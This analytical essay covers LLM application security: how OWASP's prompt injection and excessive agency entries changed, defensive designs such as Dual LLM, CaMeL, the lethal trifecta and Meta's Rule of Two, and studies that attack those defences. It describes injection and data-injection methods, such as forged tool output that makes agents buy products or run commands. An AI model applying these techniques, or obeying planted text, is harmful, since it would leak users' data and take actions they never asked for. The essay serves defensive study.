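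More than 370 people had joined by the time version 0.5 came out, about five weeks after the announcement. OWASP said this version kept and improved half of the entries in ChatGPT's original draft and replaced the rest. Membership eventually approached 500, with over 125 active contributors from AI companies, security firms, cloud providers and universities. They wrote up 43 possible threats, according to OWASP (Infosecurity Magazine's figure is "over 45"), and chose ten in several rounds of voting. Smaller teams then worked on each entry and opened it to public comment.

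The project seems to have attracted little notice among people who study the long-term risks of AI. *New reference standard on LLM application security started*, a post on the Effective Altruism Forum, reports finding no mention of it on that forum or the Alignment Forum.

John Sotiropoulos, a member of the core group, told Infosecurity Magazine that prompt injection came first because developers face it whatever model they use and however they use it, while insecure plugins ranked lower because not every application has plugins. When risks are ranked by how widespread they are, one that does slight harm to every application could outrank one that ruins a few. Many of the voters had probably learned about the subject from the same few blogs, so their votes were less independent than the number of voters suggests.

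OWASP released a draft in May 2023 and an update, version 0.5, on 1 July, according to Trend Micro's *Top 10 AI Security Risks According to OWASP*, written that summer. Trend Micro's *What are the OWASP Top 10 risks for LLMs?* dates version 0.5 to May, but the version 0.5 document gives 1 July as its date of first publication and cites a paper from June.

### From filtering to containment

The table shows how the prompt injection entry changed and where excessive agency ranked. Excessive agency is OWASP's name for giving an LLM system more functions, permissions or autonomy than its task needs.

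| Edition | Date | Prompt injection entry | Excessive agency |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.5 | 1 July 2023 | Recommends least privilege, but also filtering the input | 8th |
| 1.1 | 16 October 2023 | Drops filtering, admits that no prevention inside the model is certain, suggests ChatML | 8th |
| 2025 | November 2024 | Treats jailbreaking as a form of prompt injection, covers images and other media | 6th |
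| 2026 | August 2026 | Assumes that attacks will succeed, adds examples with agents | 3rd |

In version 0.5, OWASP (2023) advised developers to use "robust input validation and sanitization" against malicious prompts. Validation checks that input has the expected form, and sanitisation removes or neutralises dangerous parts. Both are standard practice in web security. A web form that asks for a year of birth can reject anything but four digits, but an email assistant has no comparable rule because a legitimate email can contain almost any sentence. The same entry also gave better advice, telling developers to limit the model's privileges and treat the model as an untrusted user.

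Version 1.0 followed on 1 August 2023, and version 1.1 in October. Ads Dawson of Cohere, a language model company, led the work on version 1.1, which dealt with 35 community suggestions, according to OWASP's *Announcing the LLM Top 10 version 1.1 Update* (2023).

Input validation had now disappeared from the measures against prompt injection. In its place, OWASP (2023) explained that LLMs do not separate instructions from external data and that there was therefore "no fool-proof prevention within the LLM". The entry went on to recommend:

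- giving the model its own credentials with the least access it needs
- asking the user before privileged operations such as sending or deleting email
- marking untrusted content, for example with ChatML
- treating the model as an untrusted user and leaving final decisions to a person
- checking inputs and outputs by hand from time to time, which the entry conceded was "not a mitigation"

Most of this advice is about limiting damage, and it is still sound. ChatML, however, was a poor example even for the modest purpose of reducing the influence of untrusted text, because its labels applied to whole messages. They could not by themselves identify a web page that the application had pasted into a user's message.

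The entry also described the theft of chat data through images, but none of the five measures would have stopped the browser from requesting the image. The entry on output handling linked to Samoilenko's report of the attack and recommended encoding the model's output, but neither entry recommended restricting which hosts images could come from. Microsoft had added that restriction to Bing Chat four months earlier. The 2026 edition added programs that fetch outside material automatically, and terminals that execute escape codes, to the entry on output handling. That entry fell from fifth place to tenth in the same edition.

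Trend Micro's overview of the 2025 edition repeats the edition's warning that neither fine-tuning nor retrieval-augmented generation, both popular techniques, removes prompt injection. Fine-tuning is further training on specialised material. In retrieval-augmented generation, the application searches a collection of documents and adds relevant passages to the model's input. The warning about retrieval proved apt two months after OWASP published it, when Aim Labs reported EchoLeak, which worked because Copilot's search retrieved an outsider's email.

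In the 2026 entry, OWASP goes further and now considers it most effective to design the surrounding system on the assumption that attacks will eventually get past the model, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. *なぜ今、OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 2026を読むべきか 第2回* (2026), a column by the Japanese IT company NTTデータ先端技術, quotes at length the entry's description of what OWASP calls "trusted-surface indirect injection". In this attack, the attacker writes somewhere that is open to anyone but trusted by staff, such as a support ticket or a feedback form. An employee's assistant reads the ticket and then uses the employee's access to leak code or export a database, which the attacker could never have done directly.

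Dave Hayes of the identity software company FusionAuth overstated the change when he told ReversingLabs that the 2025 edition still left some hope for a model that could resist being fooled, whereas the 2026 edition assumes every model will be fooled. Version 1.1 had already stated in 2023 that prevention inside the model was not certain. But the 2026 edition is much clearer about what a developer should do as a result.

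### Is jailbreaking prompt injection?

Version 0.5 defined direct prompt injection without mentioning jailbreaking. Version 1.1 equated the two in the phrase "Direct Prompt Injections, also known as 'jailbreaking'". Willison objects to the general habit of equating them, not to OWASP in particular. Blue41's *Prompt Injection 101*, published on a KU Leuven university site, likewise says that the two terms "represent different concepts" even though people use them interchangeably.

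The distinction matters because the remedies differ. A customer who persuades a shop's chatbot to grant an unauthorised discount has overridden the shop's instructions, but may not have broken any of the model maker's rules. The shop can prevent this by requiring discounts to be approved by its ordinary software. It can do much less about jailbreaks, because a model's resistance to them depends mainly on how the maker trained it.

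The 2025 edition stopped equating jailbreaking with prompt injection and called it a form of prompt injection in which the attacker makes the model disregard its safety rules entirely. Schulhoff had publicly given up much the same view earlier in 2024. *LLM01:2025 プロンプトインジェクション (Prompt Injection)*, a Japanese translation of the edition's entry, explains that developers can reduce prompt injection with safeguards in the system prompt and in how they handle input, but that preventing jailbreaks requires continual updates to the model's training and safety mechanisms.

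This assigns responsibility more sensibly than version 1.1 did, but it oversimplifies the division. Training also helps against prompt injection, as the 6,000 failed emails to Irarrázaval's assistant suggest. The safeguards OWASP assigned to developers in that passage are also the weak ones. A developer has more control over the assistant's tools than over how the model interprets a prompt.

SC Media describes the change as a shift from a narrow definition in 2023, closely tied to jailbreaks, to a broader one in 2025 that separates direct from indirect attacks more clearly. The 2023 versions were not quite so narrow, since both 0.5 and 1.1 defined indirect injection separately, and 1.1 also called the model a confused deputy. The full entry covered attacks by third parties, but a developer who stopped reading at "jailbreaking" might have concluded that the only danger came from misbehaving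 users.

### What the entry cited

The prompt injection entry in version 1.1 has 12 references. Seven are posts by practitioners, four are research papers, and one is a vendor document, OpenAI's description of ChatML. Rehberger wrote three of the posts and Kai Greshake wrote two. The other two posts came from the security firm Kudelski Security and from AI Village, a community of AI security specialists.

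Greshake also led one of the four papers, *Not what you've signed up for*, so half of the references came from Rehberger and Greshake. They were a reasonable choice, because both had demonstrated attacks on real products and later events confirmed much of what they described. Still, an entry with hundreds of contributors relied heavily on the work of two people. The list includes nothing by Willison, even though the entry uses the name he popularised.

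Two of the other papers show that the confusion over terms had practical effects. One proposes a defence against jailbreaks, and the other describes automated attacks that make a model produce content its maker has forbidden. Both concern jailbreaking, and a developer would learn little from either about a hostile web page. That leaves two research papers on attacks against LLM applications.

Wilson told ReversingLabs that the risks had been purely theoretical when OWASP first made the list. That is true of large-scale crime, but OWASP's own references included Rehberger's posts, which demonstrated working attacks on ChatGPT plugins, and the output handling entry cited a record of the LangChain flaw that let an attacker run code. The early entries had good evidence that attacks were possible but almost none about how often each kind occurred, which is needed to rank them.

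### Excessive agency

Excessive agency has been on the list since version 0.5, which said that LLMs "should not self-police" and that developers should put the controls in the interfaces a model uses. Version 1.1 named three causes, which the email assistant illustrates. If its only job is to summarise messages, a tool for deleting them is excessive functionality. A login that opens every employee's mailbox is excessive permission. Sending replies to customers without anyone's approval may be excessive autonomy. The developer can remove the tool, narrow the login or add an approval step without knowing why the model might go wrong.

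That last point makes the entry unusually broad. A hostile email can cause an assistant to delete messages, but so can an ambiguous request or an ordinary mistake by the model. The recommended measures limit the damage in all three cases.

Ranking excessive agency eighth was defensible in 2023 under the group's criterion, because most LLM applications could only produce text. It was poor guidance for the few developers already building agents, for whom the risk deserved to be near the top, but a single ranking cannot suit both groups. Jeremy London of Keeper Security told ReversingLabs that the entry's rise reflects how companies now deploy AI, with agents that remember earlier sessions and can change files or call other services.

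NTTデータ先端技術 notes in a column that OWASP changed little in the entry itself when it moved the entry to third place, and concludes that risks OWASP had long described were now appearing in practice. If that is right, the advice was already good years before OWASP ranked the entry high enough to show developers it was urgent.

Larry Maccherone, founder of the software company Lumenize, disputes the new rank. He told ReversingLabs that "the cure for excessive agency is more agency", arguing that an AI system needs enough freedom to find and repair its own faults, so restricting it will leave it less secure. His view conflicts with OWASP's less than it seems to, because OWASP's term covers only agency beyond what the task requires. An agent that repairs software needs permission to change that software, but not access to the payroll.

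Maccherone's argument about how companies will respond is better. He expects them to add more approval steps, and he points out that nobody can approve an agent's behaviour in advance when the agent generates it afresh each time. Any control that has to predict what an agent will do has this problem, but limits on access avoid it. In Hayes's example, an agent that can reach only one record cannot expose the whole database, whatever it does.

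### Adding incidents to the vote

OWASP released the 2026 edition at the start of August and reported in a press release that it was downloaded more than 10,000 times in the first 48 hours. Eric (2026), in *OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 全覽*, found that the project's main page still presented the 2025 edition as the latest on 5 August and a week later. The new edition was on a separate resources page, so some people looking for it would have missed it.

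The main change was in the method. The project collected 7,714 records from public vulnerability databases and a database of harm caused by AI. It then built classifiers, programs that sort text into categories, to read them. They found enough detail in 6,639 records, or 86%, to assign them to a type of risk. In the final ranking, the members' vote counted for 75% and the incidents for 25%:

combined score = 0.75 × vote + 0.25 × incidents

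The following scores, on a scale from 0 to 10, are invented to show how the weighting works.

| Risk | Vote | Incidents | 75/25 weighting | Equal weighting |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Prompt injection | 10 | 2 | 8.00 | 6.00 |
| Excessive agency | 7 | 8 | 7.25 | 7.50 |
| Misinformation | 3 | 9 | 4.50 | 6.00 |
| Output handling | 5 | 2 | 4.25 | 3.50 |

A one-point lead in the vote offsets a three-point deficit in incidents, so prompt injection stays first in this example despite its low incident score. Misinformation moves slightly ahead of output handling, which voters rated higher, but remains far behind the top two. Excessive agency would take first place if incidents counted for more than a third of the total.

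The project's leaders said that the list is a consensus product and that one noisy year of data should not overturn practitioners' judgement. This is a reasonable argument for caution, but it does not explain why the share should be a quarter instead of a tenth or a half. The choice of share could decide the order where the vote and the incidents differ as much as they do for prompt injection.

Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) gives the most detailed account of where they differed. Prompt injection, which tops the final list, would have fallen out of the top ten if risks had been ranked by incidents alone. At least ten other risks must therefore have had more recorded incidents, and since the list has only nine other entries, at least one of those risks was left off.

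Accounts of where the vote and the data agreed are less consistent. In the OWASP (2026) press release, Michael Bargury of the agent security company Zenity calls excessive agency the clearest case of agreement. Invicti makes the same claim, but elsewhere in the same article it calls sensitive information disclosure, ranked second, the only entry on which the two fully agree.

OWASP uses the term "misinformation" for false or misleading output that looks credible enough to influence a person or another program. It ranked near the bottom in the vote but near the top in the incident record, the reverse of prompt injection, and it rose from ninth place to seventh. Invicti gives the example of a coding assistant that invents a critical vulnerability and files a ticket about it, after which an engineer might spend three hours looking for it.

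Mend.io's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* suggests that security practitioners think mostly about attackers and so overlook failures that involve none. That is plausible, given who voted. Mend.io, which sells tools for checking AI-written code, also says these failures are the most expensive, but the incident counts only show how often OWASP found each type of failure, not how much it cost.

### Why the count for prompt injection is low

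OWASP attributes the low count to a "defense effect". It argues, in a passage that Infosecurity Magazine quotes, that "teams fight injection hard", so fewer successful attacks reach a public database and the count understates the risk. Invicti restates this more strongly, saying that low counts mean the defences are working.

This explanation has some merit. Recent models resist many attacks that would have worked on earlier ones, and even a weak detector will stop a careless attacker. But the low count is not itself evidence for the explanation. OWASP would presumably have taken a high count as proof that prompt injection was dangerous. If a low count also proves the danger, by showing that people are fighting it, then no count could be evidence against the ranking.

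The defence effect should also apply to other risks. Companies have spent decades and a great deal of money protecting confidential data, yet sensitive information disclosure ranks high in both the vote and the record. OWASP would need to show why strong defences keep one risk out of the databases but not the other. The argument also assumes that the defences work, but Nasr and colleagues broke most of those they tested. Good protection could therefore explain the low count only if few real attackers try as hard as they did.

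Under-reporting has better support. A weakness in a company's own assistant may never get an entry in a vulnerability database, and a vendor that runs its product on its own servers can fix it without one. Vendors have also rejected reports of prompt injection, as OpenAI and Anthropic at first did with some of Rehberger's. In 2023, Sotiropoulos said the CVE system would have to change to handle flaws that attackers exploit in ordinary language. Some thefts also go unreported because they leave nothing for the victim to notice.

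Misclassification could hide even reported attacks, because one attack can belong to several of OWASP's categories. Someone could reasonably file EchoLeak under prompt injection, output handling or information disclosure. An attack using the LangChain maths flaw began with a malicious prompt, but the flaw's CVE record describes arbitrary code execution. Version 0.5 made the overlap explicit by calling insecure output handling "a type of prompt injection vulnerability".

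A diagram in the 2026 edition supports this suspicion. Eric describes it as three rings, with ways into a system in the outer ring, things that make an attack worse in the middle ring and the resulting harm at the centre. Excessive agency and output handling are in the middle ring, though the diagram allows them other roles too. When a planted instruction makes an over-privileged agent delete files, the description of the incident will probably focus on the deletion. If the classifier gives that record a single label, it may count the incident under excessive agency instead of prompt injection. That would also make the vote and the record appear to agree about excessive agency more than they should.

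Criminals may also not have used prompt injection much. Most known thefts from AI products are demonstrations by researchers. But this can explain only part of the low count, because a vulnerability database records flaws whether or not anyone has exploited them. Researchers could have added many prompt injection entries even if no crimes had occurred. Calling such records "incidents" is therefore misleading. Even if the count is low because attacks have been rare, it may be a poor guide to the future, since SQL injection attacks took more than a decade to peak.

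The choice of databases probably affects the ranking as well. Databases of AI harm collect cases such as a chatbot inventing a legal precedent, which is unlikely to get a vulnerability record. A weakness in a software package is more likely to appear in the vulnerability databases. The relative positions of misinformation and prompt injection may therefore depend partly on how many records came from each source, which doesn't measure how dangerous either one is.

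Of these explanations, under-reporting and misclassification have the most independent evidence, and both would leave prompt injection more common than the record suggests. That supports OWASP's decision to keep it at the top, but not the claim that the defences are working. OWASP could test that claim by asking its members for logs of blocked attempts. If teams are blocking many attacks, the logs should include them. OWASP could also label each incident by both how it began and the harm it did, then check whether prompt injection was still missing from the top ten.

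## Design rules that limit what an agent can combine

In its 2026 edition, OWASP tells developers to assume that attacks will succeed and to design the system around the model accordingly. Willison proposed one such design in April 2023, splitting an assistant into two models so that the one with the tools never reads a stranger's text. Researchers later turned his proposal into a working system, and he and Meta each published rules on the same theme, short enough to remember. In tests, these designs have resisted attacks better than detectors have, but the strictest one stopped the agent from finishing most of its ordinary work.

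### Two models instead of one

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, assumed that nobody would soon stop models from obeying instructions in the text they read, and asked what kind of assistant developers could still build responsibly. In his design, a privileged model takes the user's requests and can use tools, while a quarantined model reads untrusted text and cannot. The controller between them is ordinary software that stores untrusted text under labels and shows the privileged model only the labels.

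If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the process runs like this:

1. The controller passes the request to the privileged model.
2. The privileged model asks for the latest email and chooses a label for it, such as `$VAR1`.
3. The controller fetches the email and stores it under that label.
4. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`.
5. The controller puts the email's text into a prompt for the quarantined model, stores the answer as `$VAR2`, and tells the privileged model only that the summary is ready.
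6. The privileged model asks the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

If the email tells the assistant to forward the user's password-reset messages, the quarantined model may well follow the instruction, but it can only write text, so the user gets a strange summary and no messages are forwarded. The privileged model could forward them, but it never receives the instruction.

Willison allowed an exception when the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list, such as "urgent" or "not urgent", because the controller can check that the answer is on the list before passing it on. A stranger might still get a message marked urgent, but couldn't get any other text through.

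He called his own solution "pretty bad". An attacker can still use a summary to manipulate the user, for example into pasting a block of scrambled private data into the attacker's website. The design is also complicated to build, and a single programming mistake that lets a stranger's text reach the privileged model would undo the protection. It also suits some requests poorly. The assistant can add a meeting to the calendar if an email is an invitation, because the quarantined model can answer yes or no, but it can't do whatever Julia's email asks, because the model with the tools never receives the email's text.

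### Tracking where data came from

The pattern had another gap, which Willison learned of only two years later. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, a 2025 paper from a Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich team, described the gap and introduced a system called CaMeL. Willison (2025) repeats the paper's example in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. A user asks the assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting, and adds that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The privileged model plans this correctly without seeing the notes. But the quarantined model has to read them to find the address, and a planted line can make it return the attacker's address instead, so the unchanged plan sends the document to the attacker.

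CaMeL keeps the two models, and *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), a paper on systems with several agents, calls it "a concrete instantiation of the Dual LLM pattern". The difference is that the privileged model writes its plan as a short program in a restricted form of Python. For Bob's document, a simplified version might be:

```
notes = find_meeting_notes()
address = quarantined_model("Find Bob's email address", notes)
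title = quarantined_model("Find the document's title", notes)
send_email(to=address, attachment=fetch_document(title))
```

CaMeL runs this program in its own interpreter, which tags each value with its source and who may read it. `address` counts as untrusted because it came from `notes`, which an outsider may have influenced. Before `send_email` runs, the interpreter checks the tags against a policy. The policy might allow emails to any address the user already trusts and require the interpreter to ask the user about any other. The interpreter would then ask about the attacker's address, even though the quarantined model has been fooled and no part of the system has detected an attack.

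The developers tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, the simulated workplace that Nasr and colleagues later used to break detectors. According to *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026), CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks under attack, compared with 84% for an agent without a defence. No attack within the test's scope succeeded. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens.

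CaMeL does not try to prevent misleading text, such as a false summary. Its developers also demonstrated two side channels, which leak data through the way a program behaves. In one, the attacker triggers an error that reveals information.

The CaMeL paper says that prompt injection is "not fully solved". Somebody has to write and update the policies, and users who are asked too many questions will start approving everything. Willison shared this worry, adding that after two decades in application security he still hadn't fully mastered Amazon's permission settings. He still considered CaMeL the first credible defence he had seen that did not simply add more AI.

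### Six patterns and their costs

Developers who can't adopt a new interpreter have simpler options. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, June 2025) describes six. The group, from universities and companies including IBM and Google, doubted that a general-purpose agent built on current models could offer reliable guarantees, so they asked which narrower agents could be both useful and safe. Their guiding principle is that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must be unable to trigger any harmful action.

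| Pattern | How it works | Cost or remaining risk |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees the results | It can't discuss or act on anything it fetches |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before reading anything untrusted | Planted text can change what goes into those calls, and the agent can't change its plan |
| Map-reduce | A separate model without harmful tools reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | A hostile file can get itself wrongly counted, and the agent loses all other detail |
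| Dual LLM | The model with tools handles untrusted text only through labels | The quarantined model can return a false value |
| Code-then-execute | The model writes a program, which then runs on the untrusted data | Planted text can still alter the content that the program sends |
| Context minimisation | The system deletes the user's request before the model writes its answer | The answer can't draw on anything else in the request |

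The last pattern deals with attacks by the user. A customer might ask a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and slip in an instruction to grant a large discount. If the system turns the request into a database search and then deletes the request, the model no longer sees the instruction when it writes the quote.

A fixed plan gives more protection when the user specifies more. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example request "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe". The assistant can decide to read the calendar and email John Doe before it sees any calendar entries, so a planted entry can change the message but not the recipient. A fixed plan would not have protected the address in the request about Bob's document, because that address came from untrusted notes.

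"Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections" works through ten sample applications to show which patterns fit each one. An email and calendar assistant could use plan-then-execute, the Dual LLM pattern or code-then-execute. For a software engineering agent, which has to read a lot of outside material and act on it, the paper suggests only the Dual LLM pattern.

### The lethal trifecta

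All of these patterns are for people who build agents. By 2025, many users were assembling their own by connecting a chatbot to tools from different makers, and Willison pointed out that neither CaMeL nor the six patterns could help them. On 16 June 2025 he gave them a warning they could apply without reading any code. An agent is open to data theft if it combines three abilities, which he named the lethal trifecta:

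- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content
- a way to communicate externally that could carry the data out

The email assistant has all three, since it reads the user's mailbox, strangers can email it, and it can send mail. Willison advises removing at least one. He usually recommends removing the ability to send data out, because an assistant that can't read private data or outside text is much less useful.

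It can be hard to spot which tools can send data out, however. In September 2025, Abi Raghuram showed that an agent in the note-taking product Notion could leak a client list through its web search tool. The tool accepted web addresses as well as search terms, so hidden text in a PDF could make the agent give it an address that contained the list. A user checking Notion against the trifecta would probably have counted web search as a source of untrusted content but not as a way to send data.

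To guard against this, Anthropic had restricted Claude's page-reading tool to addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned, or that were linked from pages the tool had already opened. Paul's attack on Claude's memory exploited the permission to follow links. It used a website with a link for each letter of the alphabet, and Claude spelled out the user's name by following one link after another. Anthropic then stopped the tool from following links on pages it had opened.

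OpenAI took a stricter approach in June 2026 with Lockdown Mode, an optional ChatGPT setting that limits outgoing network requests. OpenAI says planted instructions can still reach the model and make its answers wrong, but the setting is meant to block the last step of a data theft, when the data is sent out. Willison liked that the limits do not rely on a model's judgement, but he inferred from the setting's existence that ChatGPT's defaults offer no robust protection against determined data thieves. Stuckey, OpenAI's security chief, said it was for people at higher risk, who would lose some functions in exchange for the protection.

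The trifecta covers only data theft. A stranger's email could make an assistant delete the user's whole mailbox, even if the assistant had no way to send data anywhere. Willison acknowledged in November 2025 that his rule leaves out such attacks, and he considered some of them even nastier than data theft.

### Meta's Rule of Two

He was responding to Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), published on 31 October, which extends the trifecta to harmful actions. It also borrows from a rule that Google's Chrome team uses for code that handles untrustworthy input. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within one session:

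- it processes untrustworthy input
- it can access sensitive systems or private data
- it can change state or communicate externally

"Changing state" means altering something, for example by deleting a file or making a payment. An agent that needs all three properties should not run on its own, and needs at least a person's approval or another reliable check.

Meta shows three ways to apply the rule to an email assistant. The assistant could read only messages from trusted senders, work in a test environment without real data, or send mail only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft. Someone who wants an assistant for an ordinary mailbox would probably choose the last.

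Meta also describes three other hypothetical agents. The table applies both rules to them.

| Agent | Lethal trifecta | Rule of Two | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|---|
| A travel assistant searches the web, knows the user's details, and books and pays | Complete, so restrict which addresses it can contact | All three properties, so also ask the user before each booking or payment | The user approves a bad booking |
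| A research assistant opens any website and fills in forms, but has no access to the user's accounts | Incomplete, because it has almost no private data | Two properties, so it may run alone | It submits harmful forms or leaks details from the user's request |
| A coding agent changes a company's live systems, but reads only material by trusted authors | Incomplete, because it reads no untrusted content | Two properties, so it may run alone | The filter lets hostile text through, or the agent makes a mistake |

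The two rules lead to similar conclusions here, but they would differ if the coding agent changed slightly. Suppose it is allowed to read bug reports from the public, and the company blocks all its outgoing connections. The trifecta is then incomplete because no data can leave. But a planted bug report could still make the agent delete a live database. The Rule of Two covers this risk because the agent reads untrusted text, reaches sensitive systems and can change them.

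Willison called the rule the best practical advice available, but soon objected to Meta's diagram, which marked every pair of properties as "safe". He argued that an agent combining untrusted input with the ability to change state could do harm even without access to private data. Mick Ayzenberg, a security researcher at Meta, replied that the access property covers any sensitive system as well as private data, so an agent without such access can act only on systems that don't matter to its user's security. Meta also changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk".

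The reply answers the objection but makes the rule harder to apply, because a developer now has to judge which systems matter. It also covers only the user's security. Meta's research assistant can send forms to any website, so a planted instruction could make it post abuse or flood a charity's contact page without harming the user. Meta does list spam among the threats the rule does not address, along with agents' mistakes and false statements in their answers.

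Counting within a session can also miss an attack that spans several sessions, each of which satisfies the rule. Rehberger's attack on Copilot's memory showed that an instruction planted in one conversation can take effect in a later one. A developer can close this gap by treating a memory as untrusted if the agent wrote it after reading untrusted text.

The travel assistant example also shows that, under the rule, restricting an ability counts much the same as removing it. The assistant can still book and pay, and it satisfies the rule only because a person confirms each action. Two agents that both follow the rule can therefore differ greatly in safety, depending on how good their controls are.

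### Attacks on defences outside the model

Until 2026, most evidence for controls outside the model came from fixed lists of attacks. Narisetty and colleagues warned that the same kind of test had made detectors look strong until Nasr and colleagues attacked them properly. There is still reason to expect these controls to do better, because a fixed rule that forbids a payment will forbid it on every attempt, while a model's resistance can wear down with repetition. Anthropic's own figures for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks show attacks succeeding 4.7% of the time with one attempt and 63.0% with a hundred.

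Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent, which checks each tool call against rules about which tools the agent may use and what values it may pass to them. Ordinary code checks the calls, but a language model writes the rules and can loosen them during a task. Progent's developers had reported that it cut attack success on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. Narisetty and colleagues targeted the model that writes the rules, using planted text that presented the harmful action as a routine, already approved step.

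The agent and the rule-writer both ran on Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model. The researchers paired eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo settings with every attacker goal in that setting, and ran the study three times. The table gives the average attack success rates.

| Setting | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
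| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Office work | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent clearly helped against the standard attack. The adaptive result is harder to interpret, because the attack designed to beat Progent did worse on average than the standard one. The researchers suspect that its milder wording also made the agent less likely to follow it. If so, the low figure may reflect a weak attack as much as a strong defence. They did not try to reach the attacker's goal using only actions the rules already allowed, which is probably the more promising approach. They work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools on the same principle as Progent, but they are open about these limits.

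The protection reduced the share of tasks the agent completed under the standard attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and each task needed about 15 times as many calls to a language model.

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested ten defences against a more persistent attacker. Its program has a language model write a planted text, measures only how often the text succeeds, and prompts the model for a better one. With GPT-4o-mini as the agent, five of the defences had kept the success rate of standard attacks near zero. The improved attacks got through all of these except Progent. The success rate against PIGuard, a detector, rose from 0% to 28.0%. GPT-4o-mini is an old model, so the ranking of the defences is more informative than the percentages.

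In the same study, attacks succeeded much more often when the user named no action and told the agent to do whatever a document said. Such requests are particularly hard to protect with controls outside the model, because those controls can't block everything the user doesn't want until what the user does want has been specified.

### What the controls cost in realistic work

CaMeL's 77% came from AgentDojo, a test that suited it. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) found that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan after reading something. When asked to pay a particular bill, for example, the agent can list every step in advance. Real websites also contain instructions that the agent should follow, such as a checkout page's request to log in first. *DRIFT* (2025), which introduced a rival defence, had already reported that CaMeL completed none of six open-ended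 AgentDojo tasks.

Li and colleagues built 60 tasks in which the agent must replan and follow at least one helpful instruction from a third party. The tasks average about seven steps, twice as many as AgentDojo's, and involve more tools. Combining them with attacker goals gives 560 test cases. CaMeL and DRIFT became much less useful on these tasks because they depend heavily on the initial plan. Progent also became much less useful, because accurate rules are harder to write when there are more tools. Li and colleagues concluded that almost every defence they tested was either insecure or too restrictive for real use.

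Attackers can also get around these controls, which aim to stop untrusted text from becoming an instruction, by disguising the text as trustworthy data. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) examines this method. For example, an email tool returns each message with its sender, which the mail service supplies, and its body, which the sender writes. If the body imitates the tool's format, the model may treat part of it as another message from someone the user trusts. The agent then continues the user's task using forged information.

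In tests, the attack worked on Claude in Chrome and two other browsing agents. A fake product review imitated the entry for a "Read More" button but carried the number of the page's real "Buy Now" button, so an agent that tried to read more reviews bought the product. The attack also worked on Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI. A stranger's comment on a software project appeared to come from its maintainer, and the agents ran the command it recommended. OpenAI, Google and Anthropic acknowledged the reports.

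The researchers then ran 108 data injection attacks on a version of AgentDojo with GPT-5.2 as the agent. For comparison, they also ran 935 ordinary attacks that planted instructions. Data injection often worked, while the ordinary attacks succeeded only 0.2% of the time, even without an added defence.

| Defence | Method | Data injection success |
|---|---|---|
| None | Relies on the model's training | 49.1% |
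| Prompt Guard 2 | Screens text for attacks | 50.0% |
| IsolateGPT | Plans before reading untrusted text | 40.7% |
| Random names | Adds an unpredictable code to each field name | 28.7% |
| CaMeL without policies | Separates the two models | 25.0% |
| CaMeL, normal | Also tracks data | 23.1% |
| Progent | Checks tool calls against rules | 22.2% |
| CaMeL, strict | Also tracks indirect influence | 0.0% |

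CaMeL without policies is essentially Willison's Dual LLM pattern. Its 25.0% result reflects the weakness that the Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich team had identified in 2025. The quarantined model extracted false values, and the rest of the system used them. The result for normal CaMeL reflects a programming error more than the design, because the software lost track of where a value came from when the quarantined model extracted it. Choi and colleagues reported the error to CaMeL's developers. Willison had warned of this kind of mistake in 2023, when he said that a complicated design would be easy to get wrong.

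Strict tracking stopped every attack, but the agent completed only 36.5% of its ordinary tasks, compared with 86.5% without a defence. Progent kept this figure at 81.4% and random names at 83.3%. Random names also need no second model. ChatGPT's Atlas browser resisted the "Buy Now" attack because it already gave page elements unpredictable identifiers. Random names don't help when the agent processes a whole list, for example by adding up transactions that include a forged one.

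How much strict tracking limits an agent depends on its job. An agent that pays invoices from a fixed list of suppliers makes few decisions based on text from strangers, so a developer can write its policies in advance and block everything else. A general email assistant regularly has to act on strangers' messages, so its developer must either accept some risk or send doubtful cases to the user, which works only if the user reads them.

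## The Model Context Protocol and its advice on human approval

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is now the usual way to connect LLM applications to tools, and it too relies on the user to stop dangerous actions. Since Anthropic released it in November 2024, its specification has recommended that a person be able to refuse any tool call. In April 2025, security testers showed that a hostile tool could steal data even when the application asked for approval first. The maintainers have revised the rules on logins three times since then, but the advice on approval is still only a recommendation.

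### How a tool reaches the model

With MCP, the maker of a service writes one program, called a server, that any application following the standard can use. The part of the application that communicates with servers is called the client, though people often use that word for the whole application, such as Claude Desktop or the coding tool Cursor. Willison (2025) points out in *Model Context Protocol has prompt injection security problems* that a server, despite its name, usually runs on the user's own computer.

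When the client connects, it sends a `tools/list` request. The server replies with each tool's name, a description and the inputs the tool accepts. A simplified entry might be:

```
name: send_email
description: Sends an email from the user's account
inputs: recipient, subject, body
```

The client copies these entries into the context window so that the model has a list of what it can request. When the model picks a tool and fills in the inputs, the client sends the server a `tools/call` request and adds the result to the context window. The first version of the specification's page on tools (Model Context Protocol, 2024) calls this design "model-controlled".

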